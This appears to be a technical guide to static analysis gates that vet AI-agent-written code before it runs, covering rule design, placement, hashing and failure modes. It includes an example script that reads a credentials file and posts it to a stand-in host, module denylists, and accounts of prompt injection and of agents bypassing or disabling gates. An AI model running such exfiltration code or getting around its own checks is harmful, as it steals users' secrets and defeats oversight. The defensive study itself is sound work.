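# Static analysis gates for code written by language models, and how to test them against malicious samples

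## What a static analysis gate is and what it is meant to stop

An AI agent is a language model that acts for a user through software tools, and many agents write code as part of their work. When a user wants a chart of last month's sales, for example, the agent writes a short Python script, runs it a few seconds later and reads the output. Often no human reads the script before it runs. A static analysis gate checks the script first, without running it, and allows it to run only if it passes.

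Some research systems already have such gates. *SpatialClaw* (2026) describes an agent for spatial reasoning that writes its code in small cells. Before a cell runs, an analyser checks it for file access, network access and the functions `exec` and `eval`, which execute text as code. If it finds any of these, the cell does not run, and the agent gets an error message so that it can revise the code. *CaveAgent* (2026) uses three rules: one for imported modules, one for dangerous function calls, and one for object attributes that could let code escape its restrictions.

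At that moment, the gate applies a policy that a person wrote in advance to a program that no person has seen. Without it, little besides the model's own training and the process's permissions protects the machine from the model's output. NVIDIA's *How Code Execution Drives Key Risks in Agentic AI Systems* argues that more protection is needed because the model follows instructions from untrusted input, so the code it writes deserves no more trust than that input.

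### From source text to a syntax tree

A gate could simply search the script for suspicious words. The trouble is that a word search also matches comments and harmless strings, and it cannot tell a function call from a variable that happens to have the same name. Most gates therefore work on a syntax tree, the tree of statements, calls and names that a parser builds from source code. Take a program of two lines:

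```python
import shutil
shutil.rmtree("/home/ana/report/tmp")
```

`shutil` is a module of Python's standard library for handling files, and its function `rmtree` deletes a folder with everything in it, without asking for confirmation. The parser first cuts the text into tokens (names, brackets, dots, strings) and then fits the tokens to the grammar of the language. Python's *ast* module gives any program access to this parser, and prints the resulting tree like this:

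```
Module(
    body=[
        Import(
            names=[
                alias(name='shutil')]),
        Expr(
            value=Call(
                func=Attribute(
                    value=Name(id='shutil', ctx=Load()),
                    attr='rmtree',
                    ctx=Load()),
                args=[
                    Constant(value='/home/ana/report/tmp')]))])
```

The module's body has two statements. One imports `shutil`. The other is an expression that calls `rmtree`, an attribute of the name `shutil`, with one constant argument, the path. (`Load` means that the program reads the name and does not assign to it.) None of this code has run yet, so the folder has not been deleted.

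A check then walks the tree and stops at the nodes it has rules for. PyCQA's *Bandit*, an open-source security scanner for Python, builds a tree from each file and runs small plugins on the nodes. The example plugin in Bandit's *Test Plugins* takes only a few lines. It runs at every `Call` node, looks for a forbidden name in the function's full name and, on a match, returns an issue with a severity and confidence level. A similar plugin for `shutil.rmtree` would find the call above, and because expression and statement nodes carry their line numbers, the message could point to line 2.

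A gate built on this module should parse with the same Python version that will later run the script, because the grammar can change with each release. Otherwise the gate may reject valid programs, or read a different tree from the one the interpreter will execute.

More elaborate analysers examine more than one node at a time. *Static Analysis Guidance for Secure LLM Code Generation* (2026) explains that CodeQL stores the whole program in a relational database and follows data from one function into another, so it can connect a value a user typed with the place where the program uses it.

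### Reading a program and watching it run

All such methods are static analysis because none of them runs the program. Dynamic analysis runs the program and records which files it opens, which addresses it contacts, and which processes it starts.

Static analysis and trial runs can each reveal information that the other misses. Suppose the call to `rmtree` is inside a condition that holds only on the first day of the month. The tree contains the call whatever the date, but the program would look harmless in a trial run on the ninth. If the script instead reads the path from a configuration file, the tree contains a variable name in place of the constant. The analyser can then report that the program deletes a folder but not which one, whereas a trial run would show which folder it deletes.

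Watching what a program does also carries a risk for an agent, because the program has to run. A trial run of a script that deletes files will really delete them unless the script runs in a sandbox, an environment that limits what a running program can reach. A static check examines the code without running it, so it doesn't need a sandbox.

### Malicious, vulnerable and accidental

People ask gates to stop three rather different things, and much confusion about whether a gate "works" comes from running them together.

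Malicious code is designed to do harm. One definition in the glossary of NIST, the US standards institute, is software "intended to perform an unauthorized process" that damages the confidentiality, integrity or availability of a system. Vulnerable code is written without harmful intent but has a flaw that an attacker could later exploit. Accidental damage occurs when a program does the wrong thing as it runs, though nobody meant any harm and no attacker is involved.

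Most existing scanners look for vulnerable code. Chennabasappa, Nikolaidis and colleagues give a typical example in *LlamaFirewall* (2025), their paper on Meta's open-source guardrails for agents. A developer wants to filter users by email domain, and the coding agent writes a database query that inserts a visitor's text directly into an SQL command. The code works, but a visitor who types a fragment of SQL instead of a domain can change what the query does. The flaw is recognisable in the source as a string of SQL joined to a variable, and Bandit's rule B608 checks for it.

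A script can steal a developer's cloud passwords by opening the file that holds them and posting the contents to an outside server. Opening a file, reading it and sending a web request are all ordinary steps. Two of Bandit's plugins check web requests. B113 flags a request without a timeout, and B501 flags one that skips the check of the server's certificate. Neither checks what the request contains or where it goes. A script that backs up a settings file to the company's own server can have the same syntax tree except for two constants, the path and the address. A vulnerability scanner can therefore work correctly and report nothing about the theft, because the theft is not a flaw in the script.

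A small change to the two-line program above can cause accidental damage. If the program is supposed to clear the temporary folder but the model leaves off the end of the path, the constant becomes `/home/ana/report` and the program deletes the user's report. The syntax tree still has the same shape. Bandit's list of plugins has no entry for deleting files. A gate's author could add one, but the rule would match the correct script as well as the wrong one, because telling them apart requires knowing what the user wanted, which isn't in the code.

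Bandit's documentation presents it as a tool for finding vulnerabilities. Its instructions for writing a new plugin begin with identifying a vulnerability to test for, and the message for its `eval` rule, in *blacklist calls*, recommends a safer function, which is advice for an honest programmer. *DySec* (2025), which covers the detection of malicious packages in Python's public package index, lists among existing tools bandit4mal, a fork of Bandit in which Vu added patterns for malicious code. The fork suggests that Bandit's original rules did not cover malicious code.

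The two targets overlap. Malicious programs often use `exec` or start a shell, and Bandit flags both, so a scanner for vulnerabilities will catch some malicious code. But it will flag the same constructs in legitimate code, and its flags don't distinguish the two. The standard catalogues don't supply a pattern for malicious code either. The Common Weakness Enumeration, MITRE's public list of software flaws, has an entry for SQL injection that a scanner can tie to a definite rule. Its entry for malicious code, *Embedded Malicious Code*, covers a product with code that "appears to be malicious in nature", and nobody can turn that description into a rule about nodes in a syntax tree.

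Which of the three deserves most attention depends on what happens to the code. If a script runs once on the user's own data and is then discarded, an attacker has little time to exploit an unsafe query, but theft or a wrong deletion does its damage in that single run. An unsafe query matters more in code that goes into a product, so CodeShield, the static analyser in *LlamaFirewall*, rejects it when the agent submits its change. *LlamaFirewall* lists insecure coding and malicious code as separate risks. It relies on CodeShield alone for insecure code, and on CodeShield together with two other scanners for malicious code that an attacker induces. The paper also names malicious code execution among the behaviours that future versions should cover.

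### How harmful code comes to be written

The most direct route is a harmful request, where the person typing the prompt wants to cause damage and either asks for it openly or disguises the request. NVIDIA's security testers used disguised requests against an internal data analysis tool that used the PandasAI library to turn plain English questions into Python and run the result. They worded their questions so that the model returned code they had chosen, which the application then ran on its own machine. The flaw received the identifier CVE-2024-12366 in February 2025. PandasAI filtered the code before running it, but the testers got past the filter, so this is also an example of a failed gate.

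In other cases the user is innocent and the instructions come from material the model reads, such as a web page, a document or a comment in someone else's code. This is called prompt injection. Chennabasappa and colleagues measured how often it succeeds in recorded runs of ten models on AgentDojo, a benchmark of 97 tasks with attacks planted in the output of the agents' tools. Without a guardrail, the attacks succeeded in 17.6% of cases. This shows that agents obey planted text often enough to matter, but it is weak evidence about how often injection leads to harmful code, because the planted instructions were all of one style and the benchmark does not specifically test generated programs.

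A model can also copy a bad example without malicious intent. *LlamaFirewall* describes a scenario in which an agent copies an unsafe query from a popular web post that presents it as legitimate advice. A filter for hidden instructions correctly finds none in the post.

Generated code can also contain plain mistakes. *STELP* (2026), which describes a system that intercepts generated code before it runs, gives the example of a flight-booking plan that contains an infinite loop and a call to a tool the model invented. Calling an invented tool usually just produces an error, but the loop can tie up the machine. *STELP* labels the loop a malicious attack on the machine's resources, though a model can also write such a loop by mistake, by leaving out the step that advances a counter.

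A gate has access only to the program, not to this history, so its decision must depend on what the program would do. The history matters to whoever tests the gate, because hostile code, unlike careless code, may be disguised to get past it. A rule that stops nearly every accidental deletion may stop few deliberate ones, so a good result on accidental deletions is poor evidence of how well the rule stops deliberate ones.

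### Verdicts and errors

A scanner produces findings, and a gate has to turn them into a decision. Three verdicts are possible:

- *Allow*: the program runs.
- *Ask*: the program waits until a person has looked at it and decided.
- *Deny*: the program does not run, and the agent may get the reason.

The checks in *SpatialClaw* and *CaveAgent* only allow or deny code, without the option of asking a person. Asking suits a construct such as `rmtree`, which is sometimes right and sometimes disastrous, but it works only if someone is there to answer. If an agent runs overnight, asking either has the same effect as denying or leaves the agent waiting a long time. People who get such questions all day will also probably start approving them without reading them.

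A gate can disagree with these verdicts in two ways. It can let a malicious program through (a *miss*) or refuse a benign one (a *false block*). Anyone who also wants the gate to stop accidents has to count accidentally destructive programs as harmful too, and say so before the test begins.

No gate can avoid both misses and false blocks on every possible program, because no algorithm can always correctly decide whether an arbitrary program will ever do some particular thing. This follows from the halting problem, which was proved unsolvable in the 1930s. A gate could eliminate misses by denying everything, or false blocks by allowing everything, but it would be useless either way, so every real gate is a compromise between the two.

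What counts as benign depends on the agent's job. *SpatialClaw* rejects `.to_csv`, the usual way to save a table, but this does little harm because its agent answers questions about images and rarely needs to save tables. The same rule would often block legitimate work by a data analysis agent. Other false alarms come from defects in a rule. In *From Language Models to Control Policies* (2026), a model writes small control programs and 29 static checks examine them. One security check fails to recognise names that the program defines in a helper function nested inside another function, so it repeatedly raised warnings about harmless code. These were only warnings, but a gate that denied code on any finding would have wrongly blocked the program each time.

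A false block gets noticed because an agent stops working and someone complains, but a miss produces the same "allow" verdict as harmless code. *SecDrift* (2026), a study of security flaws in AI-generated code, ran two scanners, Bandit and Semgrep, on every sample and counted a sample as vulnerable if either flagged it. Bandit flagged 515 samples, and Semgrep flagged only 363 of these. Each of the other 152 is either a flaw that Semgrep missed or a false alarm by Bandit, and the flags alone do not show which. The study therefore does not treat unflagged samples as secure. Measuring how much a gate misses requires running it on programs already known to be harmful.

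## Placing the gate between writing the code and running it

A gate on one route doesn't check programs that take another. An agent might send the script for the sales chart straight to a Python tool, save it as a file and run it from a shell, keep it as a reusable tool for next month, or submit it to the company's repository. The information available to a gate also differs between these routes.

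### Places to intercept code

*SpatialClaw* puts its check in the code-execution tool, the point closest to execution. The tool parses each cell and walks the syntax tree, then uses regular expressions to look for patterns that the tree rules can miss, such as methods that write files. The cell reaches the kernel, a Python process that stays alive between cells, only after both passes. At this point the language is known, the full text of the cell is available, and the gate can use the parser of the same interpreter that will run it.

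A gate that checks notebook cells before the kernel runs them has no access to what the agent does with its other tools. Checking one cell at a time is also harder because the kernel keeps functions and variables from earlier cells. If a cell contains only `clean(folder)`, its syntax tree doesn't show what `clean` does or what `folder` contains. The gate can recover some of this information by keeping the earlier cells and analysing the new one with them.

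A hook covers more tools. It is a program that the agent's framework runs at a fixed point, here before every tool call, and it receives the tool's name and arguments. The call waits for the hook's decision. *Before the Tool Call* (2026) lists such hooks in several frameworks, including Claude Code (Anthropic's coding agent), Cursor and LangChain. Because the framework, not the model, runs the hook, an injected instruction that persuades the model to request a harmful call does not bypass the check.

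Sage, an open-source tool from the security company Gen Digital, uses these hooks. According to Help Net Security's *Open-source tool Sage puts a security layer between AI agents*, it intercepts shell commands, web requests and file writes. It compares them with a list of dangerous patterns, looks up the reputation of web addresses, and checks whether a package exists in its registry and how old it is. A syntax tree doesn't contain this package information, since an install command looks the same whether the package is ten years old or was published today. Gen Digital also argues, though this is not a test result, that a tool on the user's machine can use the session history to tell a legitimate deletion from a hijacked agent's attempt to hide what it did.

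The arguments of a tool call may contain very little code. With the command `python clean.py`, the hook receives the file's name but not its contents, so it has to read the file to judge the program. A hook on file writes could have checked the contents earlier if the agent created `clean.py` with its file-writing tool, but that hook would not have fired if the file came with a downloaded repository or was written by another program.

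A gate can also sit between the agent and the model and read the messages they exchange. Invariant Labs' *Code Validation* describes such guardrails, which developers can add without changing the agent. One example rule uses Semgrep to scan the Python code in calls to the `ipython_run_cell` tool and raises an error if Semgrep reports any finding. The example program for this rule reads a line of input and runs it as an operating system command. A second rule does the same for Bash commands sent to the `cmd_run` tool, and its example downloads a script and feeds it directly to a shell.

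Both rules name the tool they apply to, so a new tool that runs code under a different name has no gate until someone writes a rule for it. In the download example, the script is on a remote server, so the gate can check only the command that fetches it and can do little except refuse all commands of that kind.

Some agents save code as a tool that they or other agents later call by name. A check at registration covers the whole definition and can use a slow analysis because it runs only once per tool. But the arguments of later calls are not yet available. A tool that deletes whatever folder it receives has the same code whether a call passes a temporary folder or the user's home directory, so each call also needs its own check.

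Registration also creates a stored copy that someone could later change. *A Deterministic Control Plane for LLM Coding Agents* (2026) addresses this problem for agent definitions in a shared registry by giving each entry a SHA-256 hash, a short fingerprint of its bytes that changes if any byte changes. The installer recomputes the hash of the fetched entry and aborts if it doesn't match. The design also stamps its list of installed entries using a secret key, but according to the paper, a hostile process under the same user account could read the key and forge the stamp. An agent normally runs under the user's account, so the gate's records are safer under a different one.

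The last opportunity to check the code comes when the agent proposes a change to shared code. GitHub's *Threat Detection* describes a check of the agent's patch and pull request at this stage. By default, an AI model checks for prompt injection, leaked secrets and malicious patches, and users can add further steps after it, such as a static scanner. A gate here can examine the complete change in context, and a delay of a few minutes does little harm. But agents usually run their code to test it before they submit it, so the check protects the repository and the people who use its code but comes too late to prevent damage to the machine the agent works on.

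### Closing the other paths

If an agent's Python tool has a gate but its shell doesn't, the agent can write the code to a file and run it from the shell. It can do this without hostile intent, since trying another tool after the gate blocks its code is a natural next step for a model that is supposed to finish its task.

Part of the answer is to send every tool call through a single gateway that checks it. The Model Context Protocol (MCP), which Anthropic introduced in late 2024 as a common interface between agents and tools, makes this fairly easy because every call uses the same kind of message. But *Governed MCP* (2026) points out that the specification doesn't require the agent's host program to make a safety check before it calls a tool. The operating system also doesn't stop an agent that controls the host program from skipping the check.

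A gateway for tool calls also does not control what a program does once it is running. A script that has passed the gate can start a second program without any tool call, so either the rules have to cover constructs that start other programs, or the sandbox has to prevent scripts from starting them.

The gate's settings also need protection. Anthropic documents that Claude Code reads its hooks from JSON settings files, and Gen Digital's *sage openclaw* describes a configuration file in the user's home folder with switches for individual checks. An agent with permission to edit such a file could turn off its own gate, perhaps while trying to fix what it thinks is a broken environment.

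A builder can test for ways around the gate with a harmless program that the rules must refuse, such as one that calls `eval` on a constant and prints the result. The builder tries to run it through every tool the agent has: typing it into the Python tool, saving it and starting it from the shell, registering it as a tool, and calling it from another script. If the program prints its result, that route bypasses the gate.

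### Running the text that passed the check

Even on a single path, the program may change between the check and the run. Security engineers call this a time-of-check to time-of-use gap. It exists whenever the gate reads and approves a file that another process later reopens.

The simplest remedy is to read the program once and run what was read:

```python
try:
    source = open(path, "rb").read()
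    findings = check(ast.parse(source))
except Exception:
    refuse("The gate could not analyse this program.")
else:
    if findings:
        refuse(findings)
    else:
        run(source)
```

Here `run` receives the bytes that the gate has just parsed, so a later edit to the file has no effect on this run. *Mind the Gap* (2025) applies the same idea to agents' tools in general. It replaces pairs of tools, where one checks something and the other acts on it, with one tool that does both in a single operation. It combines this with a monitor and with rewritten prompts that discourage risky sequences. According to *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (2026), a review of the field, the combination reduced the share of runs with a gap between check and action from 12% to 8% on a benchmark of 66 tasks. The remaining 8% is a good reason to build the check into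 the tool that runs the code rather than depend on the agent's plan.

Sometimes the check and the run have to be separate steps, for example because a person has to approve the program or because the approval should last for weeks. The approval then has to identify the content it applies to. The gate stores a hash of the program when the program is approved, computes the hash again before the run, and refuses to run the program if the two differ. A file name or the text of a command doesn't identify the content, since `python clean.py` stays the same when `clean.py` changes.

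A hash of one file is often too little. Suppose the script that clears the temporary folder takes the path from a local module:

```python
# clean.py
import shutil, settings
shutil.rmtree(settings.TMP)

# settings.py
TMP = "/home/ana/report/tmp"
```

If someone shortens the path in `settings.py` after the approval, the hash of `clean.py` remains correct and the script deletes the whole report.

In *When the Approved File Is Unchanged*, Hossen (2026) measured how often this happens in 20 public repositories where an approved file, usually a deployment or release workflow, depends on other files. Among 5,251 commits (recorded changes), 542 changed at least one file that the run reads. Of these, 296 (54.6%) left the approved file itself untouched, so a check on its hash would have accepted them. These were ordinary commits, with no attacker involved. The percentage depends heavily on one repository,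 which supplied 130 of the 296 commits, and without it the share falls to 43.6%. Hossen also chose the repositories because they split their work over several files, so the figure applies to such projects, not to the average script an agent writes.

His remedy is to approve the whole set of files that the run is configured to read. He calls an approval *sound* if it covers every file in that set, and *exact* if it also covers nothing else. To compute one hash for the set, the gate sorts the file paths, lists each path with the hash of its file, and hashes the list. If a tool loads a whole folder, the list has to include the folder's contents so that adding a file changes the hash. About one commit in ten would have required renewing the approval.

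Deciding which files belong in the set is the difficult part. Hossen asked two coding agents, Codex CLI and Claude Code, to write such approval records, and they computed the hash correctly in 61 of 62. But in 16 runs on one deployment with Terraform, a tool that creates cloud resources from text files, they chose five different sets of files. Two of those records contained none of the Terraform files but had the same form as the others and a correct hash, so a gate that relied on the agent's records would have accepted any later change to the deployment. Hossen concludes that the gate should compute the hash itself and take the list of files from a source it can verify, such as the tool's own record of its inputs or a list that people have reviewed.

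For Python, the gate can build much of the list from the syntax tree. It looks for a workspace file that matches each import, then repeats the search in each file it finds. This method misses imports that the program assembles while running. The gate can instead include every Python and settings file in the project folder, which is cruder and covers more, but unrelated edits then trigger a new check.

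Hashing these files only shows that nobody has changed them. The gate also has to apply its rules to them, because a harmless-looking script can call a local module that contains malicious code. If a Python program starts a shell script, the gate must either have rules for shell scripts or block the call.

### When the gate itself fails

A gate may fail to parse a program, run out of time or memory, or crash because of a mistake in a rule. In each case, the program has not passed the check and should not run. The short program above therefore rejects the code after any exception.

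Gen Digital states that Sage is "designed to fail open", which means that the agent's action goes ahead if something inside Sage goes wrong. A reasonable argument for this is that developers install the tool voluntarily and would soon remove it if its bugs stopped their work. But the argument holds only while failures are accidental, and an attacker who can influence the code may be able to cause a failure deliberately to get past the check.

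A gate can also fail open by accident. Hooks in Claude Code return their result as an exit code, the number a program returns when it ends. In a 2025 version of its documentation, Anthropic lists 0 for success and 2 for blocking the call, while any other code shows an error to the user and lets execution continue. A Python program that ends with an unhandled exception returns 1, so a Python hook that crashes on an unusual script lets the script run. A hook can catch every exception and return 2, but this doesn't help if the process dies before the handler runs, as can happen when a very large or deeply nested program crashes Python's parser. The process that calls the gate should therefore run the code only after an explicit "allow". Because products change their failure behaviour between versions, it is worth crashing the hook on purpose to check whether the code still runs.

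Syntax errors need separate attention because an analyser that cannot parse a program may return an empty list of findings, as it would for a clean program. For this reason, *Static Analysis Guidance for Secure LLM Code Generation* had to discard candidate programs that did not parse. Invariant Labs provides a separate flag for syntax errors, and one of its example rules refuses any code with that flag. Its parser also has a mode for notebook commands that are not valid in ordinary Python. Without this mode, the rule would refuse valid cells that use those commands.

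### How much delay a check adds

A gate that checks every program adds its running time to every step, which creates pressure to keep it simple. CodeShield, the analyser in Meta's LlamaFirewall, reduces the delay by scanning in two passes. All code goes through a fast pass of pattern matching and light analysis, which takes about 60 milliseconds. Code it flags goes on to a more thorough analysis, which takes about 300 milliseconds on average. Chennabasappa and colleagues report that about 90% of inputs need only the fast pass.

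If *p* is the share of inputs that need the second pass, the average delay is

*t*₁ + *p* · *t*₂ = 60 + 0.1 × 300 = 90 milliseconds.

If the 300 milliseconds already include the fast pass, the average is 84. An agent that runs twenty scripts in a task would wait slightly less than two seconds in total. The average depends heavily on *p*, though, and doubles to 180 milliseconds for an agent whose ordinary work triggers the first pass 40% of the time.

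These are Meta's own figures from its internal deployment, so they describe code written by Meta's systems on Meta's hardware. Meta's product documentation, *CodeShield*, gives a more cautious figure of under 100 milliseconds for the fast pass, and adds that inputs that need deeper inspection can take longer than 300. Even so, the delay is small compared with the time the model takes to write the code. In the experiments of *Static Analysis Guidance for Secure LLM Code Generation*, the fastest model took between 1.2 and 3 seconds to write a program, so 90 milliseconds would add between 3% and 8%.

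The thorough analysis runs only on code that the fast pass has flagged, so it can clear up false alarms but cannot catch anything the fast pass missed. A builder who copies this design should therefore make the fast pass over-sensitive and accept a higher *p*.

### Refusing, or returning the finding for revision

When the gate refuses to run a program, it can report only the refusal, or it can explain what it found and let the agent try again. The error message in *SpatialClaw* names the forbidden module, function or pattern, in the same form as an ordinary runtime error. A limit on consecutive failures stops the agent from retrying indefinitely. If the agent has merely used a forbidden way of saving a table, an explanation is clearly better than a bare refusal, because the agent doesn't have to guess what was wrong.

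How well models use such findings is a question that *Static Analysis Guidance for Secure LLM Code Generation* examined in detail. The study looked at vulnerable code and not at malicious code. It compared seven strategies:

- *Baseline*: the model writes the program without guidance.
- *Self-Refine*: the model criticises and revises its own program, and no analyser takes part.
- *FDSP*: the model receives Bandit's report on the finished program and repairs it until Bandit finds nothing. This comes closest to what a gate does when it returns its findings.
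- *FDSP (Semgrep)*: the same with Semgrep in place of Bandit.
- *PromSec*: a trained network guides the rewriting, with the number of Bandit's findings as its score. The model never gets the report.
- *Comment*: Semgrep runs after every line the model writes. On an alert, the system deletes the last block of code, inserts the warning as a comment, and lets the model continue from there.
- *Steering*: the same, except that the warning goes into the prompt, together with a recommended fix.

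The researchers tested three models, two from the Qwen2.5 family and the larger DeepSeek-V4.1-flash, on three sets of Python tasks. RiskyPy has 73 tasks, selected because analysers flag typical solutions. SecEvalPlus has 140 tasks, and many of their weaknesses have no recognisable pattern in the syntax. BaxBench contributed 84 web applications, which the researchers ran and attacked with real exploits. They judged whether programs were secure using security tests for SecEvalPlus, the exploits for BaxBench and a language model for RiskyPy, and never used the analysers for this. The language model agreed with two human experts on 74% and 72% of a sample, and the experts agreed with each other on only 66%, so the RiskyPy results are the least certain of the three.

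The table gives the share of DeepSeek's programs that both worked and were secure, in percent.

| Strategy | SecEvalPlus | BaxBench | RiskyPy |
|---|---|---|---|
| Baseline | 31.4 | 38.9 | 52.5 |
| Self-Refine | 31.2 | 37.7 | 63.5 |
| FDSP | 31.2 | 2.4 | 66.2 |
| FDSP (Semgrep) | 30.2 | 24.6 | 61.6 |
| PromSec | 29.3 | 38.1 | 44.7 |
| Comment | 34.3 | 38.9 | 45.7 |
| Steering | 34.8 | 28.6 | 64.4 |

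On RiskyPy, FDSP and Steering produced clear gains. But Self-Refine came within three points of the best result without any analyser, which suggests that much of the benefit comes from having the model review its code. On SecEvalPlus, no difference from the baseline was statistically significant. Neither Qwen model improved significantly with any strategy on any of the three sets. Steering used at most 1.5 times as many tokens as the baseline with the Qwen models and 1.7 times as many with DeepSeek, whereas PromSec used up to 24 times as many. But running Semgrep after every line made DeepSeek take 3.4 to 9.6 times as long.

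Most of the losses on BaxBench come from one Semgrep rule, which is against accepting connections on all network interfaces. The applications needed this setting so that the tests could reach them from outside the container. The Steering prompt told the models to follow a recommendation only if it did not conflict with the task, but they still removed the required setting in 79 of 83 cases, which the study calls overcompliance. With FDSP, the share of DeepSeek's applications that worked at all fell from 65.9% to 2.4%.

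A false alarm from the gate can therefore do more than delay the agent. If the gate returns the finding, the model may write a program that passes the check but no longer does its job, and the failure may surface only after deployment. The study recommends filtering out alerts that conflict with the task before they reach the model, because telling the model to ignore them was not enough.

Whether a model can fix a finding also depends on the repair required. Replacing an unsafe XML parser with a safe one takes a small local change. DeepSeek fixed this problem in 30 of 99 cases and broke the program in 2. Removing `eval` usually means restructuring the code around it. DeepSeek managed this in 21 of 33 cases without breaking anything, while the larger Qwen model succeeded in 2 of 63 and broke 23 working programs.

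Semgrep and Bandit together missed between 94.4% and 95.8% of the working but insecure programs in SecEvalPlus, depending on the model. They missed about two thirds of DeepSeek's exploitable applications on BaxBench, and between 6% and 20% on RiskyPy, whose tasks were chosen to suit the analysers. Their alerts were also a poor indication that a program was insecure. Of DeepSeek's working BaxBench applications, 41.0% were exploitable, compared with 38.6% of those with an alert.

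On RiskyPy, four analyser-guided strategies were each compared with the baseline for three models. Guidance significantly increased the share of working programs without alerts in all twelve comparisons, but significantly increased the share that were actually secure in only two. Repeated revision selects for programs that the analyser accepts, so a program that passes on its fifth attempt gives less assurance than one that passes on its first. A gate's log should therefore keep the rejected versions together with the accepted one.

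All of this applies to models that are trying to write good code. If the code comes from someone hostile, a detailed finding shows them which rule to avoid, and every retry gives them another chance to test the gate. It makes sense to decide rule by rule whether to return the finding. The gate can return it for constructs that harmless programs often contain but can easily do without. If a rule detects something the agent's job never requires, such as reading stored passwords, it is safer for the gate to refuse without explanation and alert a person.

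The gate's message can also carry an attack if it repeats text from the program, because the model will read that text. *From Tool Orchestration to Code Execution* (2026) describes error messages with embedded instructions that manipulate the model's next attempt, and has a second model screen the messages before the agent receives them. A static gate can avoid most of this problem by building its messages from fixed phrases, a rule name and a line number, without quoting the code.

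## Writing the rules: denylists, allowlists and restricted languages

The short program in the last section reads a script once and runs the bytes it has checked, but it does not define the function `check`. That function takes the syntax tree and returns a list of findings, and its rules determine which programs the gate stops.

### Walking the tree

The usual algorithm goes over the tree twice. The first pass collects the imports to determine which module each name belongs to. The second works out the full name of every function the program calls and looks it up in the policy.

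```
judge(source, policy):
    tree = parse(source)              # on any error: DENY
    names = {}                        # name in the program -> full name
    findings = []

    for node in walk(tree):           # first pass: imports
        if node is "import M as A":
            names[A] = M
            if policy refuses M: add (node.line, rule) to findings
        if node is "from M import F as A":
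            names[A] = M + "." + F
            if policy refuses M.F: add (node.line, rule) to findings

    for node in walk(tree):           # second pass: calls
        if node is a call:
            full = resolve(node.func, names)
            if policy refuses full: add (node.line, rule) to findings

    return DENY, findings  if findings is not empty
    return ALLOW           otherwise

resolve(expr, names):
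    if expr is a plain name N:    return names[N] if it exists, else N
    if expr is an attribute X.B:
        base = resolve(X, names)
        return UNKNOWN if base is UNKNOWN, else base + "." + B
    return UNKNOWN
```

Here `M` is a module, `F` is something imported from it, and `A` is the name the program uses for it, which is the original name if the import has no `as`. The algorithm needs two passes because a function near the top of a script may use a module that the script imports further down.

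Suppose the script that clears the temporary folder begins with `import shutil as sh` and then calls `sh.rmtree(...)`. The first pass stores `shutil` under `sh`. In the second pass, `resolve` receives `sh.rmtree`, replaces `sh` with `shutil` and returns `shutil.rmtree`, which the policy can match. An import of the form `from shutil import *` doesn't list the names it brings in, so the table stays empty and a later call to `rmtree` resolves to the bare word. A policy should therefore refuse that form of import.

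`resolve` can follow names but not values. In `table.to_csv(...)`, `table` is a variable, so `resolve` returns a result with no module in it. In `open(path).read()`, `read` is called on the result of another call, and `resolve` returns `UNKNOWN`. Both are ordinary Python, and every policy has to handle them. Neither a denylist nor an allowlist has an entry for them, so a denylist lets them through and an allowlist refuses them.

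Two scripts help to compare the rule types. The first averages a column of a sales file:

```python
# average.py
import csv

with open("/home/ana/report/sales.csv") as f:
    amounts = [float(row["amount"]) for row in csv.DictReader(f)]
print(sum(amounts) / len(amounts))
```

The second sends a file of stored passwords to a server:

```python
# send.py
import requests

with open("/home/ana/.cloud/credentials") as f:
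    text = f.read()
requests.post("https://collect.example/in", data=text, timeout=10)
```

### Text patterns

The simplest rules are regular expressions, which match character sequences in the source. The pattern `requests\.post` matches the upload in `send.py` and nothing in `average.py`. Regular expressions need no parser, so a gate can also apply them to shell commands, configuration files and code in languages it has no grammar for.

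But unlike the tree walk, the pattern also matches comments, as any word search does, and it misses the upload if the program imports `post` directly and calls it by that name.

Patterns are more useful for the contents of strings. A syntax tree stores a path, a web address or a shell command as a single constant, without splitting it into parts. A gate can search only the tree's string constants, which excludes comments. One pattern might match paths containing the word `credentials`, and another might match addresses outside the company's domain. The search fails when the program assembles the string from pieces at run time. This problem affects every rule type here and is covered later.

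### Denylists on the tree

Mukherjee and Tanjim (2026), in *MoMHa*, describe a denylist for a system in which programs come too fast for a person to review. A coding agent repeatedly rewrites a *harness*, the Python program that builds prompts for a language model, sends them and parses the answers. The system evaluates about 100 versions for each of seven kinds of task. Before a version runs, a check called AST-GUARD walks its tree and refuses the following constructs:

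- *Imports*: modules for files and folders (`shutil`, `pathlib`, `glob`, `tempfile`), for the network (`requests`, `urllib`, `http`, `socket`), for the operating system and other processes (`os`, `sys`, `subprocess`, `signal`), and several more, such as `ctypes`, `importlib` and `threading`.
- *Calls*: `exec`, `eval`, `compile`, `__import__`, `open`, `input`, `breakpoint`, `exit`, `globals`, `locals`, `getattr`, `setattr` and `delattr`.
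- *Attributes*: `system`, `popen`, `Popen`, `check_output`, `listdir`, `rmtree`, `communicate` and `urlopen`.

It also requires the program to define a class named `Harness` with the two methods that the rest of the system calls.

The list bans both the `shutil` module and the `rmtree` attribute, although a program normally has to import `shutil` to call `shutil.rmtree`. The second ban helps when `resolve` can't identify the object before the dot. But a rule that matches only the attribute name also rejects unrelated objects that use it. For example, a harness might naturally store its system prompt as `self.system`. The list also bans `getattr` because it fetches an attribute by a name that the program supplies as a string, so the tree may not contain the name.

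AST-GUARD would reject both example scripts, because both call `open`. This doesn't matter for a harness, since its data arrives as an argument, but it makes the list useless for an agent that has to open sales files to analyse them. If the builder removes `open` from the list, `average.py` passes and `send.py` still fails because it imports `requests`. But if the agent also has to download exchange rates, the builder has to remove `requests` too, and then `send.py` passes and can steal the data. A denylist of this kind checks constructs one at a time, so it misses this theft, which combines two constructs that are harmless on their own.

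Mukherjee and Tanjim adjust the denylist to the task. Coding and database tasks get a *strict* setting with a short list of permitted imports, which makes the denylist partly an allowlist. Classification and fact-checking get a *light* setting, with the standard bans and a generous list of permitted modules. Mathematics gets a *minimal* setting, which permits `eval` and `compile` so that a harness can evaluate formulas, but still bans all the other calls on the list.

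The exception for `eval` weakens other bans too, because they apply to the text of the harness, while `eval` executes a string whose calls do not appear in the tree. Protection then depends on the sandbox behind the gate, which in *MoMHa* limits a run to 300 seconds and gives the program an almost empty environment. A builder who needs formulas can avoid the exception by writing a small function that parses the formula, accepts only numbers and arithmetic operators, and computes the result.

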